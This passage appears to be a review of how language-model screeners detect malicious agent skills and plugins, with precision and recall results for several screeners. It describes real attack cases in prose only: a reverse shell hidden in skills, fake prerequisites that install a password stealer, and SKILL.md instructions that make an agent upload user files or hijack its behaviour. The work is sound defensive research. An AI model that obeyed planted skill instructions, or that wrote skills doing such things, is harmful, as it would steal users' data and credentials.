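# Screening agent skills and plugins with language models: precision, recall and cost

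## Agent skills, the hubs that distribute them, and what a screener must decide

An agent skill is a folder of written instructions, often with scripts, that an AI agent follows to do a particular job. The agent is a language model that can read files, run terminal commands and call internet services. With the right skill installed, it can summarise a spreadsheet or build a slide deck without the user spelling out the steps. Anyone can write a skill, and users find them on public marketplaces called hubs. A skill runs with the permissions of the user who installed it, so a malicious one can steal passwords or give an attacker access to the machine.

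Hubs and users have responded with screeners, tools that read a skill before installation and decide whether to block it. Some match the skill's files against fixed patterns, called static rules. Increasingly, screeners use a separate language model, called the judge, to read the package and assess whether its contents fit its stated purpose. Nearly all measurements of how well screeners work date from 2026 and cover skills rather than other plugins.

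### What a skill contains and what it can reach

Every skill has a file called SKILL.md, which opens with a short block of metadata. The specification from Agent Skills, the site that documents the format, requires this block to include a name of at most 64 characters and a description of at most 1,024 characters that covers what the skill does and when to use it. Authors can add other fields, such as a list of the tools the skill may use. The instructions follow the metadata and are written in ordinary prose. A skill can also include scripts and reference documents.

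*MalSkillBench* (Guo, Jia and colleagues, 2026), a test collection of malicious skills, describes how an agent loads a skill in three stages. At the start of a session, the agent reads only the metadata. When a user's request matches the skill's description, the agent loads the instructions and follows them as guidance. It then runs any code the instructions call for. The skill's author therefore writes the text that determines both when the skill is loaded and what the agent then does.

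Installing a skill typically gives it the full privileges of the local user, with little scrutiny and few requests for confirmation, according to *Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2026). A malicious skill therefore doesn't have to break in and then widen its access, as ordinary malware often does. *Skills registry threat models* (2026) points out that a skill may also declare dependencies from several package managers at once (npm, pip and others), so one installation can run install commands from all of them because of a file the user never read.

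A plugin is any installable extension of an agent, and it can be larger than a skill. Anthropic's *Plugins reference* defines a plugin for the coding agent Claude Code as a directory that may hold skills, further agents, hooks and tool servers. Hooks are scripts that run on set events, such as each time the agent uses a tool. A tool server provides functions that the agent can call through a standard protocol, MCP. Liu and colleagues describe its code as running on a separately administered server, whereas a skill's code runs on the user's own machine. A plugin that bundles these parts has at least as much access as a skill. Kapner (2026), in *Securing Claude Code plug-ins*, says that plugins have full access to the terminal, local files and environment variables, and that most developers install them without reading any of the source.

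### Three routes of attack

An attacker can put malicious code in a skill's scripts. Liu and colleagues found a skill named math-calculator whose description offers arithmetic, but whose script calculate.py contains a reverse shell, a connection from the user's machine to the attacker's server that lets the attacker run commands on the user's machine. The technique is not new. Guo and colleagues matched the code to a malicious Python package that does the same thing with a different address.

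The instructions can carry the attack just as well. Yang, Ying and colleagues (2026), in *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs*, give the example of a skill that summarises CSV files, a common spreadsheet format. Its final step tells the agent to upload the file to an outside address to validate it. An agent that follows this step leaks the data, even if the skill's folder contains no scripts. Of the 632 harmful elements that Liu and colleagues catalogued in malicious skills, 84.2% were in SKILL.md and only 8.5% in code files. Not all of that 84.2% is prose, because SKILL.md can also contain commands for the agent to run.

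The third route splits the attack between the instructions and a script. Liu and colleagues found a near-exact copy of a legitimate skill for making slides, with 487 lines instead of the original's 484. The added lines tell the agent to run a backup script on the user's file, and the script quietly uploads the file to an outside server. Read separately, the instructions look like a sensible precaution and the script looks like an upload routine that an honest backup tool might also have. Guo and colleagues describe a more tightly coupled version, in which the agent follows the instructions to prepare a file and a script then uses that file to complete the harmful act, so neither part need look fully malicious on its own.

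### Evidence of real attacks

In early 2026, researchers at the security company Koi audited all 2,857 skills then on ClawHub, the hub for the OpenClaw agent. Koi's *ClawHavoc* (2026) lists 341 of them as malicious, 335 apparently from a single campaign, which gave the report its name. The skills posed as cryptocurrency wallet trackers, YouTube tools and automatic updaters, and 29 had names that imitated ClawHub's own. Their professional-looking documentation had a "Prerequisites" section that told the reader to install a helper program first. On Windows, the helper came in a password-protected archive, which antivirus software cannot scan. For Mac users, the section gave a command to paste in, which downloaded Atomic Stealer, a program that criminals rent by the month to steal passwords, browser data and cryptocurrency wallets.

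The malware was on outside servers, and the skill folder held little more than directions to it. By 16 February, Koi had raised its count of malicious skills to 824, and the hub had grown to more than 10,700 skills. Koi sells protection against such attacks, but Trend Micro independently identified a heavily overlapping set of skills. Guo and colleagues also gathered 703 malicious skills from public sources, 86.3% of which relied on a fake prerequisite.

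The broadest survey is that of Liu and colleagues, who in January 2026 collected 98,380 skills from two hubs, skillsmp.com and skills.rest. They narrowed these down in steps:

1. They searched every skill for 14 suspicious patterns, such as reading stored credentials or downloading and running remote code. Fixed rules covered the scripts, and the model GPT-5.2 helped with the instructions. This left 4,287 candidates.
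2. They ran each candidate in an isolated container for up to 60 seconds at a time, with fake passwords and keys planted as bait, and recorded its network traffic, system calls and file changes. Of the candidates, 762 did something that warranted a closer look.
3. Two researchers independently reviewed all 762, comparing what each skill did with what its documentation described. They confirmed a skill as malicious only when both rated it at least probably so.

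That produced 157 confirmed malicious skills, or 0.16% of the total. One actor had made 54.1% of them from a template, with each skill posing as a different commercial brand. In 115 of the 157, the reviewers found capabilities that nobody could have inferred from the public description. The hubs removed 147 of the skills within 30 days of hearing about them.

The count of 157 malicious skills could be too low or too high. Skills that matched no pattern were never run in the container, and when the researchers rechecked a tenth of the unconfirmed candidates, 93.2% of that sample had dormant triggers that the 60-second runs had not set off. Yang and colleagues, however, later reread the 157 and judged only 95 to be malicious. Koi's rate for ClawHub, 12%, is about 75 times Liu's, but Koi examined one hub during an attack and counted skills without requiring them to misbehave in a container.

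### Which hubs screen, and what a verdict triggers

Yang and colleagues mapped the screeners that public hubs run. ClawScan, ClawHub's own judge, comes from OpenClaw's documentation.

| Hub | Screeners |
|---|---|
| ClawHub | ClawHub-Mod (the hub's own static rules), SkillSpector (NVIDIA), AI-Infra-Guard (Tencent), ClawScan |
| skillmd.com | SkillMD Review, skill-scanner (Cisco), SkillSpector |
| skills.sh | Gen Agent Trust Hub, Snyk Agent Scan, Socket |
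| SkillsMP, skills.rest | none |

The last row matters because SkillsMP indexes over four million skill files, and because Trend Micro also found the skills it investigated on SkillsMP and skills.sh.

After ClawHavoc, ClawHub began screening every new skill by sending it to VirusTotal, a malware-scanning service with a language model that summarises what a package does. OpenClaw automatically approved skills judged benign, added a warning to those judged suspicious but left them available, and immediately blocked downloads of those judged malicious. When it announced the screening, OpenClaw acknowledged that a carefully written malicious instruction could get through. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, later found five malicious skills that ClawHub had left unblocked between February and May 2026.

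By June, ClawScan was making the final decision, using the other scanners' findings as evidence. A finding is one reported concern about a skill, usually with a severity. SkillSpector's findings, for example, appear on a skill's page as advice and do not block it by themselves. In a dataset of 67,453 skills that OpenClaw released that month, ClawScan had rated 25,504 (38%) suspicious and 206 (0.3%) malicious.

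The labels have since changed to Pass, Review, Warn and Malicious, according to OpenClaw's *Security Audits*, and only Malicious comes with a flat instruction not to install. A separate risk level records how much power a skill has when used as intended, so a tool for publishing posts can carry medium risk and a Review label even if nobody suspects its author. Severe findings can also lead ClawHub to hide a listing or hold back a publisher's future releases. According to OpenClaw's *Moderation and Account Safety*, a publisher whose version is blocked can download the scan results, fix the listing and upload a new version. The hub can lift a hold once it confirms a false alarm, but an honest publisher still loses time and, for a while, users.

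Flagging a skill as malicious has less effect on skills.sh, where the user still decides whether to install it. According to Vercel's *Automated security audits now available for skills.sh*, the hub removes flagged skills from its search results and leaderboard. Anyone who goes directly to a flagged skill's page sees a warning before installation, and the hub's installation tool also displays the audit results first.

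### Malicious, risky or merely badly documented

Counting a screener's mistakes requires first deciding which skills it should block. An earlier scan cited by Liu and colleagues found potentially risky patterns in 26.1% of skills, while Liu and colleagues confirmed 0.16% as malicious in their own study. The two figures come from different studies, but a screener that treated every risky pattern as an attack would block a large part of a hub to remove very few malicious skills.

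Yang and colleagues separate the cases by intent (whether someone designed the skill to compromise its user) and harm (whether the skill's behaviour can do damage, whatever its author intended).

- A skill with malicious intent is *malicious*, even if the attack would not work.
- A skill whose intent a reviewer cannot determine, for instance because it contains hidden text that nothing explains, is *suspicious*.
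- A skill with a legitimate purpose that can nevertheless do damage is *risky*.
- A skill with a legitimate purpose and no identified harmful behaviour is *benign*.

Vulnerable skills should be classed as risky. For example, a skill that tells an agent to act on comments on a proposed code change has an honest purpose, but an outsider could steer the agent by posting a comment. A well-meant skill is also risky if it relies on a command that deletes a company's live systems when run with one wrong option. A skill whose author forgot to list its permissions is benign if it does nothing harmful, even if it is poorly documented.

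Screening is difficult because intent does not appear in the files. A skill that reads a key from the computer's environment may be doing ordinary configuration or starting a theft, and a screener has to infer which from the rest of the package. Yang and colleagues left risky and suspicious skills out of their tests because the screeners do not explicitly distinguish these categories. Their scores therefore describe performance on the clearer cases, while a real hub also contains risky and suspicious skills.

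### Four measures of a screener

The best overall result in Yang and colleagues' tests went to skill-vetter, itself a skill, which guides a coding agent through a security review. With the open-weight model Qwen3.6-35B-A3B as its judge, it produced these counts:

| | Blocked | Passed |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious skills | 822 | 62 |
| Benign skills | 37 | 552 |

*Precision* is the share of flagged skills that are malicious. The screener flagged 859 skills, of which 822 were malicious and 37 benign, so its precision is 822 / 859, or 95.7%. *Recall* is the share of malicious skills that the screener flags, which is 822 / 884, or 93.0%. The *false-positive rate* is the share of benign skills that it flags, which is 37 / 589, or 6.3%. The 37 benign skills flagged by mistake affect both precision and the false-positive rate, but precision is calculated over all flagged skills and the false-positive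 rate over all benign skills.

*F1* combines precision and recall into one number, their harmonic mean:

F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall) = 2 × 0.957 × 0.930 / (0.957 + 0.930) = 0.943

F1 is the harmonic mean of precision and recall, so it stays close to the lower of the two. ClawHub-Mod, run on the same test set, blocked 66 of 886 malicious skills and no benign ones, which gives it a precision of 100% and a recall of 7.4%. Its F1 is 0.139, whereas an ordinary average of the two would be 0.54.

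All four numbers depend on the threshold, the score or severity at which a screener blocks a skill. Yang and colleagues counted a skill as blocked by skill-vetter only when the verdict was not to install it, so a milder warning counted as a pass. Precision and F1 also depend on the share of malicious skills in the test, which was 60% here, several times the share that Koi found on ClawHub at the height of the ClawHavoc campaign.

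## Comparing what a skill declares with what it does

A screener can check whether a skill's files do more than the author has declared, though it cannot read the author's intent from them. The idea comes from work on mobile apps. WHYPER (2013) searched Android app descriptions for sentences that explained why an app needed a given permission. CHABADA (2014) grouped apps by the topics of their descriptions and flagged apps that used sensitive functions unusual for their group.

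*Behavioral Integrity Verification for AI Agent Skills* (Wu, Li and Liu, 2026) applies the comparison to skills. Its method, BIV, builds one set of capabilities from what a skill declares and another from what it contains, then identifies the capabilities in each set that are missing from the other.

### Two sets and two differences

Both sets draw on a fixed list of 29 capabilities in seven categories:

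| Category | Capabilities |
|---|---|
| Network (4) | outbound web requests, other outbound connections, inbound connections, downloading and running a file |
| Filesystem (7) | reading project files, sensitive files or the home directory; writing ordinary or sensitive files; listing files; deleting files |
| Process execution (4) | starting programs, directly or through a shell; running text as code, in a fixed or a dynamic form |
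| Environment (3) | reading one environment variable, all of them, or sensitive ones |
| Encoding (3) | base64 encoding, cryptography, compression |
| Credential (3) | reading, creating or transmitting a credential |
| Instruction-level (5) | overriding the agent's instructions, concealing actions, changing the agent's identity, acting silently, telling the agent to send data out |

The declared set, D, holds the capabilities that a skill's metadata and descriptions communicate. The actual set, A, holds the capabilities in its code and instructions. A mismatch between them can go in either direction:

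- *Undeclared capabilities* (A − D) are in the code or instructions but not in the metadata. The user has had no chance to agree to them.
- *Unused declarations* (D − A) are in the metadata, but nothing in the skill uses them. They often look like leftovers from a copied template.

BIV classes both undeclared capabilities and missing advertised features as deviations. Undeclared capabilities matter more for security, since a skill that silently reads passwords is more dangerous than one that lacks a feature it advertises.

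BIV classifies text by its content, not by the file it is in. In one real skill, which presents itself as a messaging integration, the metadata file contains text telling the agent to use the skill for every question and never to ask the user anything. BIV treats this text as instructions and puts it in A. Otherwise, a hijack would count as declared behavior if its author wrote it in the metadata.

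### How BIV fills the sets

Program analysis and a language model, Claude Opus 4.6, both contribute to each set. For D, a parser reads the metadata fields, manifest files and SKILL.md headings, while the model reads the prose descriptions. For A, program analysis covers the scripts and the model covers the instructions.

BIV analyzes Python most thoroughly, following a value from where the script reads it, through steps such as encoding, to where it leaves the machine or runs as code. For JavaScript, TypeScript and shell scripts, BIV matches only text patterns and links them only within a single file, so it undercounts thefts in which one file reads a password and another sends it.

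A language model can also report capabilities that a skill does not have. BIV applies three filters to the model's output:

1. It discards an answer that merely repeats the list of categories from the prompt.
2. It requires a quoted passage for every capability and checks that the passage occurs in the skill, ignoring differences in spacing and capital letters. This check removes 5.7% of the capabilities that the model reports, including some real ones that it misquoted.
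3. For high-risk capabilities such as credential access, it also looks for relevant keywords near the quotation.

A genuine quotation can still fail to support the reported capability, so Wu, Li and Liu had two people check 150 deviations. Both reached a definite answer on 122, and the evidence supported the reported capability in 87.7% to 97.5% of those. The range reflects 12 cases in which they agreed on the behaviour but disagreed on its label. On a sample of 69 skills, other language models upheld a smaller share of the reported capabilities, 73.7% for Gemini 3.1 Pro and 48.5% for GPT-OSS 120B. A panel of three models, including Opus 4.6 itself, estimated that BIV finds roughly 65–70% of the capabilities present.

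### A worked example

Suppose a weather skill has the description "Gets the forecast for any city from an online weather service". Its Python script requests the forecast, but it also reads the user's cloud password from a file and sends it to a second server. In simplified form, the comparison runs as follows:

1. The language model finds one capability in the description and quotes the sentence as evidence. D = {outbound web request}.
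2. Program analysis finds three capabilities in the script. A = {outbound web request, credential read, credential transmission}.
3. Subtraction gives A − D = {credential read, credential transmission}. D − A is empty.
4. The analysis also records a path from the password file to the network call.

The skill declared the web request, so only the two credential capabilities cause deviations. The recorded path shows a reviewer how those capabilities connect.

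BIV would report the same undeclared capabilities for a harmless weather skill as for the theft if the skill's author forgot to mention that it uses a key. Many online services require a key that identifies the customer, and a script that calls one of these services has to read the key and send it.

Hidden code can also create a mismatch between what a skill declares and what it does. Wu, Li and Liu describe a real skill for editing presentations that declares reading, writing and listing files. One line in a 38-kilobyte JavaScript file decodes a block of text and runs it as code, which opens a reverse shell to the attacker's server every 30 seconds. BIV reported that both the decoding and the execution were undeclared, and gave the line number.

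### The scan of OpenClaw's hub

Wu, Li and Liu ran BIV on 49,943 skills they had collected from OpenClaw's hub in early 2026. BIV reported 250,706 deviations, of which 135,187 were undeclared capabilities and the rest were unused declarations. They then sorted the deviations into 137 groups by similarity. If skills that share a name are counted once, 80.0% had at least one deviation that fitted a group. The share rises to 91.0% if every skill is counted separately and deviations that fitted no group are included.

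A second step assigned an intent to each of 163,754 deviations. It put 81.1% down to oversight and 18.9% to hostile intent. The 81.1% includes 8,004 deviations that the step labelled ambiguous, and without them the split is 80.1% to 19.9%. The hostile share of undeclared capabilities varies widely by category:

| Category or combination | Share labelled hostile |
|---|---|
| Instruction-level | 96% |
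| Credential | 56% |
| Network | 37% |
| Process execution | 12% |
| Filesystem | 10% |
| Decoding text, then running it as code | 90% |
| Downloading a file, then running it | 86% |
| Reading data, then sending it out | 58% |
| Reading one file, then writing another | 8% |

These labels come from a classifier, and nobody checked them against what the skills' developers intended. Fifteen fixed rules labelled 45.9% of the deviations, and Claude Opus 4.6 labelled the rest. One rule labels any instruction-level capability as an attempt to hijack the agent, which explains much of the 96%. Another labels a credential combined with an outbound connection as credential theft. The benign weather skill with the undocumented key appears to match that rule.

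When the labels are combined by skill, 4,397 skills, or 8.8%, count as malicious. ClawScan gave that rating to only 0.3% of the skills in OpenClaw's June dataset. The classifier probably applies the word "malicious" much more freely, although the two scans cover different dates and ClawScan had a separate label for suspicious skills. Wu, Li and Liu describe the flagged skills as candidates for review. They separately tested BIV's detection of malicious skills on a benchmark of 906 skills, where it reached an F1 of 0.949 with Opus 4.6 as the judge.

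### What counts as a declaration

A human review found a much smaller gap. For *Do Skill Descriptions Tell the Truth?* (He, Li and colleagues, 2026), two people independently examined 4,556 skills that contain code. In 9.4% of them, the code did something relevant to security that the description did not cover. In another 24.3%, the description was only less detailed than the code. For example, it might mention producing a report but not the path where the script saves it.

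Much of the gap between 80.0% and 9.4% comes from different definitions. He and colleagues treat all of SKILL.md as the description, including the instructions, whereas BIV treats the instructions as behaviour. If the instructions openly include a shell command for the agent to run and the short description does not mention it, only BIV reports a deviation. He and colleagues also ignore unused declarations.

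The mismatches that remain under the narrower definition are often serious. The checker that He and colleagues built, which uses GPT-5, found 413 of the 428 skills whose mismatches the reviewers confirmed. In 212 of those, the code used a credential and sent it to an outside service, and the description did not cover this. He and colleagues make no claim about intent, so many of the 212 may come from honest authors who forgot to mention a key.

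The skill format gives authors little help in declaring more. Its only field resembling a permission lists the tools the skill may use. *Beyond Maliciousness* (Pandey, Singh and colleagues, 2026) examined 6,309 skills from SkillsMP and ClawHub. Of the 6,061 whose metadata could be parsed, only 770 (12.7%) listed any tools. The field cannot express access to credentials. Listing a tool can remove a confirmation prompt, but it doesn't stop the agent from using unlisted tools.

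Skill authors who did fill in the field often left things out. Pandey and colleagues used two Claude models, mostly Haiku 4.5, to infer what each skill could do, and found that 59% of the 770 declarations understated it. Studies of mobile apps and browser extensions had instead found that developers requested more permissions than they needed. Those platforms block whatever an app has not requested, so requesting too little breaks the app, while a skill works just as well with the field empty. BIV therefore has few formal declarations to work with, and much of D depends on how a language model interprets a description.

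### Tool servers with misleading descriptions

The same check applies to tool servers, which plugins may bundle. An agent receives a description of each function a tool server offers but not the code, so it relies entirely on the description when choosing a function. The protocol, MCP, does not verify these descriptions.

Li, Ma and colleagues (2026), in *Don't believe everything you read*, compared the descriptions of 10,240 tool servers with their code. Their program, MCPDiFF, traces chains of function calls in the code. A language model then summarises what each chain does and the features listed in the server's documentation. MCPDiFF converts the summaries into vectors (lists of numbers that represent meaning) and measures how much of the code's behaviour has a counterpart in the documentation.

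About 13% of servers had a match below 80%. Li and colleagues examined three in detail:

- mcpx-py, a general development framework, has an undocumented function that can shut down any process on the machine.
- longport-mcp, which connects to a brokerage service, can place and cancel real trades, but its documentation omits both functions.
- zerops-mcp has documentation that describes read-only access to GitHub, yet the code includes a function that changes user information.

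None of these proves bad intent, but each could lead an agent to take a consequential action the user did not expect. An outsider who gained access to the brokerage server could also trade with the user's money.

MCPDiFF deliberately ignores features that the documentation advertises but the code lacks. Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, extracted 19,200 functions from 2,214 Python servers and found a mismatch in 9.93% of the functions and at least one mismatch in 35% of the servers. The most common type of mismatch, 35.4% of the total, was the one MCPDiFF ignores, where the description promises more than the code delivers. Such a description can make an agent choose the wrong function, but it doesn't mean the code has hidden behaviour. A further 11.3% of functions had no description to compare.

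Shi and colleagues also found that the wording of the question changes the answer. They gave Claude Sonnet 4.5 a description and the matching code, and tested it on 400 functions that people had labelled:

| Question to the model | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| Are they consistent? | 95.9% | 47.2% |
| Are they inconsistent? | 78.8% | 100% |
| Both, with a third query if the answers differ | 96.0% | 97.5% |

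The model accepted more than half of the real mismatches when the question suggested consistency, and caught them all but raised more false alarms when it suggested inconsistency. The combined method, DCIChecker, needed the third query in 38% of cases. A re-implementation of MCPDiFF found 90 of the 197 real mismatches in the same test.

DCIChecker's recall is probably lower in practice. Half of the 400 functions were ones it had flagged, a far higher proportion than in the full dataset. It missed 5 mismatches among the 200 functions it had passed. If it missed mismatches at the same rate across all the functions it passed, its recall would be about 83%.

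### Where the comparison fails

A broad enough description can cover almost anything. If a skill "manages your online accounts", a language model may reasonably classify access to passwords as declared, and BIV's quotation check will confirm that the quoted sentence is in the description. Shi and colleagues count vagueness as a type of mismatch, with "process local files" as an example. Vague descriptions are harder to detect than other mismatches. In a test with 40 artificial cases of each type, DCIChecker caught 26 of the vague descriptions and at least 38 of every other type.

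A harmful skill also passes this comparison if its description declares the harmful behaviour. The CSV skill that uploads the user's file to an outside address could be described as "summarises spreadsheets and validates them online". D and A would then match, even though the skill would still send the data off the machine.

In *SkillPrivus*, Fernandez-Espinosa, Ngong and colleagues (2026) try to close this gap for personal data by adding a standard that the skill's author does not control. Their screener lists each operation in which a skill reads, infers, saves, sends or deletes personal information. A language model then judges each one against both the skill's stated purpose and the usual expectations for that kind of data. Health data, credentials and information other people shared in confidence must stay on the user's machine unless the skill explicitly requires consent.

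Of 563 skills that handled personal data, the screener flagged 307, or 54.5%. One flagged skill says it lets users "talk to" their Apple Health data, but its instructions send health questions to an outside service that its description does not name. The verdicts are fairly uncertain. They matched the judgments of three human annotators in 83.2% of the cases that could be resolved, but the kappa statistic, which corrects for agreement by chance, was only 0.35. People also disagree about what counts as appropriate use of personal data, so adding a standard of appropriate use to the screening brings that disagreement into the verdicts.

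The most common problem that Fernandez-Espinosa and colleagues found was data reaching a recipient that the skill's purpose did not justify. BIV cannot detect this because it records that a skill sends data over the network, but not where the data goes. *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (2026) describes a real skill that sends every matching query through a server under the attacker's control. The attacker receives the user's stock tickers and portfolio identifiers, along with any session tokens, which can give access to a logged-in account. A skill that looks up financial data needs a network connection anyway, so declaring one would not reveal the attack.

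More precise declarations would help. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (Metere, 2026) proposes a manifest in which a skill names each host it contacts and each file path it reads. The software running the agent would refuse any call that needs a capability the manifest doesn't list. The weather skill could then reach its forecast service but not a second, undeclared server. The manifest could also carry a digital signature, though Metere points out that a signature shows only who endorsed a skill, not whether it behaves as declared. Someone would still have to decide whether to trust each named host.

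Some behaviour is absent from the package. The ClawHavoc malware, for example, was never in the skill folders. BIV can report an instruction to download and run a file, but it cannot add the downloaded program's capabilities to A. BIV can also miss code that chooses at runtime which function to call, and it does not cover changes to a skill's behaviour after installation that leave nothing in the package to analyse.

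### Testing an action against the user's task

All these comparisons depend at least partly on the skill author's description of the skill. *SkillScope* (Wu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) uses the user's request instead. It classes an action as over-privileged if the request does not authorise it, or if the skill can complete the task without it. (An unrelated checker by He and colleagues has the same name.)

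The same action can therefore pass for one request and fail for another. One skill that analyses code repositories can collect details of the user's machine and send its report to an outside endpoint. This is appropriate if the user asked for those details and wants the report synchronised, but both actions exceed a request for a local summary of risky changes. Another skill, deep-work, tracks periods of concentrated work and draws a chart. It also includes instructions for the agent to send the report, network settings and traces of the user's command history to an outside Telegram account. None of this is necessary when the user asks to see last week's chart.

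SkillScope tests a skill in four steps, with GPT-5.1 as its language model:

1. It maps the actions in the instructions and scripts, and keeps those that do not clearly fit the skill's declared purpose.
2. It writes user requests that should lead the agent to each of these actions, and creates simple test files where the task needs them.
3. It runs the skill in an isolated environment, once as written and once without the action.
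4. The model judges whether the request authorised the action and whether the second run still achieved the user's goal.

SkillScope had a precision of 94.1% and a recall of 95.0% on 200 hand-labelled skills, half of them over-privileged. When Wu, Wang and colleagues replaced the two runs with a model that only read the skill, precision fell to 76.6% and recall to 82.0%. Much of SkillScope's accuracy therefore comes from running the skill, which a screener that only reads files cannot do.

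SkillScope confirmed over-privileged actions in 6,590 (9.6%) of 68,312 skills from ClawHub and SkillsMP. The actions came from instructions in 5,541 of these skills and from scripts in 1,498, with some skills having both. Many of the 6,590 may have been written without harmful intent, since a developer can easily include a step that some users don't need.

Deleting an over-privileged action is often the wrong remedy. When Wu, Wang and colleagues removed such actions from the skills in their test set, only 144 of 249 legitimate tasks still worked. When they instead rewrote the skills so that each action ran only if the user's request called for it, all 249 tasks succeeded and over-privileged actions ran 88.6% fewer times.

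SkillScope can test only the requests it generates, and it has difficulty with skills that need specialised files or a login to an outside service. Agents also behave differently from one run to the next, which makes the two runs harder to compare. A necessary action can also be unsafe. The skill that routes financial queries through an attacker's server would fail to answer if SkillScope removed the query, so the query would count as necessary. The authorisation check covers the destination, but a user who asks for a share price rarely specifies which server should supply it.

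## How findings become a verdict, and why harmless skills are blocked

Screeners often disagree about the same skill. *Skill or Threat?* (Gao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) presents four reports on voice-message, a skill that generates audio and sends requests to Feishu, a workplace chat service. The skill's instructions pass an access token to a script on the command line. Snyk Agent Scan rated this a high-severity credential risk and blocked the skill. SkillSpector reported missing user warnings, rated the problem medium and let the skill pass. Socket and Gen Agent Trust Hub also let it pass, without reporting anything about the token.

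Such disagreements are common. Gao and colleagues sorted the findings on 386 skills by attack mechanism. Counting each mechanism once per skill, they found that 79.9% appeared in only one of the four reports. Each screener also has its own rule for deciding when findings justify a block, so two screeners can produce the same findings and still reach opposite verdicts.

### Six screeners on one test set

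Yang and colleagues ran six screeners on the same skills in 2026, which makes the screeners' designs comparable. Hubs use four of them: ClawHub-Mod, skill-scanner, SkillSpector and AI-Infra-Guard. The other two, skillscan-security and skill-vetter, are community tools that had done well in independent benchmarks. The study excludes the screeners on skills.sh (Snyk Agent Scan, Socket and Gen Agent Trust Hub) because they run only on their makers' servers, where outsiders can't inspect how they work.

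Four of the six screeners can use a language model as a judge. Yang and colleagues tried each of these with Qwen3.6-35B-A3B and DeepSeek-V4-Flash, which anyone can download and run, and with OpenAI's GPT-5.4. They also ran skill-scanner and SkillSpector with their static rules alone.

The test set has 886 malicious and 591 benign skills from seven datasets. The paper's abstract gives a total of 1,147, but its tables add up to 1,477. Two of the datasets, MalWild and MalSkillBench-Wild, contain skills that researchers collected from hubs. They supply 243 of the malicious skills but only 53 of the benign ones, and the original compilers had labelled all 53 malicious. The other 538 benign skills come from benchmarks that pair harmless skills with constructed attacks. The false-positive rates below therefore depend heavily on which harmless skills five benchmark teams included.

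### Four designs and their blocking rules

The simplest design uses static rules alone. ClawHub-Mod checks every readable file against its rules, gives each match a severity and rates the skill clean, suspicious or malicious. Yang and colleagues counted only a malicious rating as a block. The rules in skillscan-security also cover combinations, such as access to a secret together with a network connection. The tool ignores findings with a confidence below 0.75, and blocks a skill if a remaining finding matches a designated blocking rule or if the combined score reaches 70.

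Cisco's skill-scanner first runs its rules and a check that follows data through shell and Python code. It then puts the skill's contents into a single model prompt, leaving out whatever exceeds a size limit, and asks for findings with a severity and an explanation. It merges the model's findings with the earlier ones and keeps the higher severity where they overlap. One high or critical finding from either source blocks the skill. Cisco's *Skill Scanner* warns that a "safe" result means only that the scan produced no such finding.

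SkillSpector, from NVIDIA, uses the model twice. Three model-based analysers read each file for particular problems, such as prompt injection (text that tries to redirect the agent) or a gap between declared and actual behaviour. A further model pass then reviews every finding, including those from the static rules, and keeps only the ones it can confirm against the file. The screener adds up points for the findings that remain. NVIDIA's *SkillSpector*, which documents an earlier version than the one in the test, gives the scale:

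- A critical finding counts 50 points, a high one 25, a medium one 10 and a low one 5.
- The total rises by a factor of 1.3 if the skill contains executable scripts.
- From 51 points, the recommendation is not to install.

A skill without scripts thus gets 50 points and a recommendation of caution for two high findings, while a skill with scripts gets 65 points and is blocked. A harmless skill can easily reach 65 points, such as the weather skill whose script sends the user's key to the forecast service. One of NVIDIA's rules covers credentials that flow into a network call and rates this critical. If the rule matches, the skill gets 50 × 1.3 = 65 points, and only the review can prevent the block.

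In the fourth design, an agent explores the files itself. Tencent's AI-Infra-Guard first collects context about the skill, then audits the code against the description in SKILL.md, and finally reviews its own findings to remove false alarms and duplicates. It subtracts penalties from a safety score of 100 but gives no verdict, so Yang and colleagues counted a score of 60 or less as a block. One high-severity finding or two medium-severity ones are enough for a block.

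The other agent-based screener, skill-vetter, is a page of instructions that Yang and colleagues had the coding agent Claude Code follow. *Skill Vetter*, published by spclaudehome, lists 14 red flags that require immediate rejection, including sending data to external servers and requesting credentials, tokens or API keys. It also puts skills that handle credentials in a high-risk class, one level below rejection, that requires a human's approval. The model has to decide which instruction applies to a harmless skill that needs a key. Yang and colleagues counted only an explicit verdict not to install as a block.

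### Pooled results

These are the results from Yang and colleagues over all seven datasets:

| Screener | Judge | Precision | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ClawHub-Mod | none | 100% | 7.4% | 0% |
| skillscan-security | none | 70.4% | 85.1% | 50.4% |
| skill-scanner | none | 81.8% | 36.1% | 12.0% |
| skill-scanner | Qwen3.6 | 88.9% | 95.1% | 17.8% |
| skill-scanner | DeepSeek-V4 | 88.9% | 94.1% | 17.6% |
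| skill-scanner | GPT-5.4 | 88.9% | 88.1% | 16.6% |
| SkillSpector | none | 81.9% | 52.0% | 17.3% |
| SkillSpector | Qwen3.6 | 93.7% | 68.7% | 7.0% |
| SkillSpector | DeepSeek-V4 | 92.6% | 85.8% | 10.3% |
| SkillSpector | GPT-5.4 | 86.4% | 94.2% | 22.2% |
| skill-vetter | Qwen3.6 | 95.7% | 93.0% | 6.3% |
| skill-vetter | DeepSeek-V4 | 95.1% | 92.4% | 7.1% |
| skill-vetter | GPT-5.4 | 82.2% | 94.6% | 30.8% |
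| AI-Infra-Guard | Qwen3.6 | 90.6% | 87.5% | 13.6% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | DeepSeek-V4 | 94.3% | 79.8% | 7.3% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | GPT-5.4 | 93.8% | 86.1% | 8.5% |

Static rules alone can miss malicious skills or block harmless ones. ClawHub-Mod blocked no harmless skills but missed nearly all the malicious ones, while skillscan-security caught most attacks but blocked half of the harmless skills. NVIDIA describes SkillSpector's static stage as having high recall and moderate precision. In this test its recall was 52.0%, and its precision was higher.

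Adding a language model raised recall for both screeners that were also run without one. The choice of model matters a great deal, but the same model can be stricter in one screener and more lenient in another. Replacing Qwen3.6 with GPT-5.4 raised skill-vetter's false-positive rate from 6.3% to 30.8%, while recall rose by less than two percentage points. In AI-Infra-Guard, the same change lowered the false-positive rate from 13.6% to 8.5%. The contradiction in skill-vetter's instructions may partly explain the difference, because a model that applied the list of red flags literally would reject almost any skill that connects to an online service.

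Other tests give skill-scanner quite different false-positive rates:

- Tencent's *Who is the strongest gatekeeper for Agents?* (2026) reports 24% with DeepSeek-V4-Flash, against 17.6% in the table. The dataset explains most of this. Tencent's benchmark, SkillTrustBench, is one of the seven that Yang and colleagues drew on, and their scores for that part alone imply a rate of about 23%.
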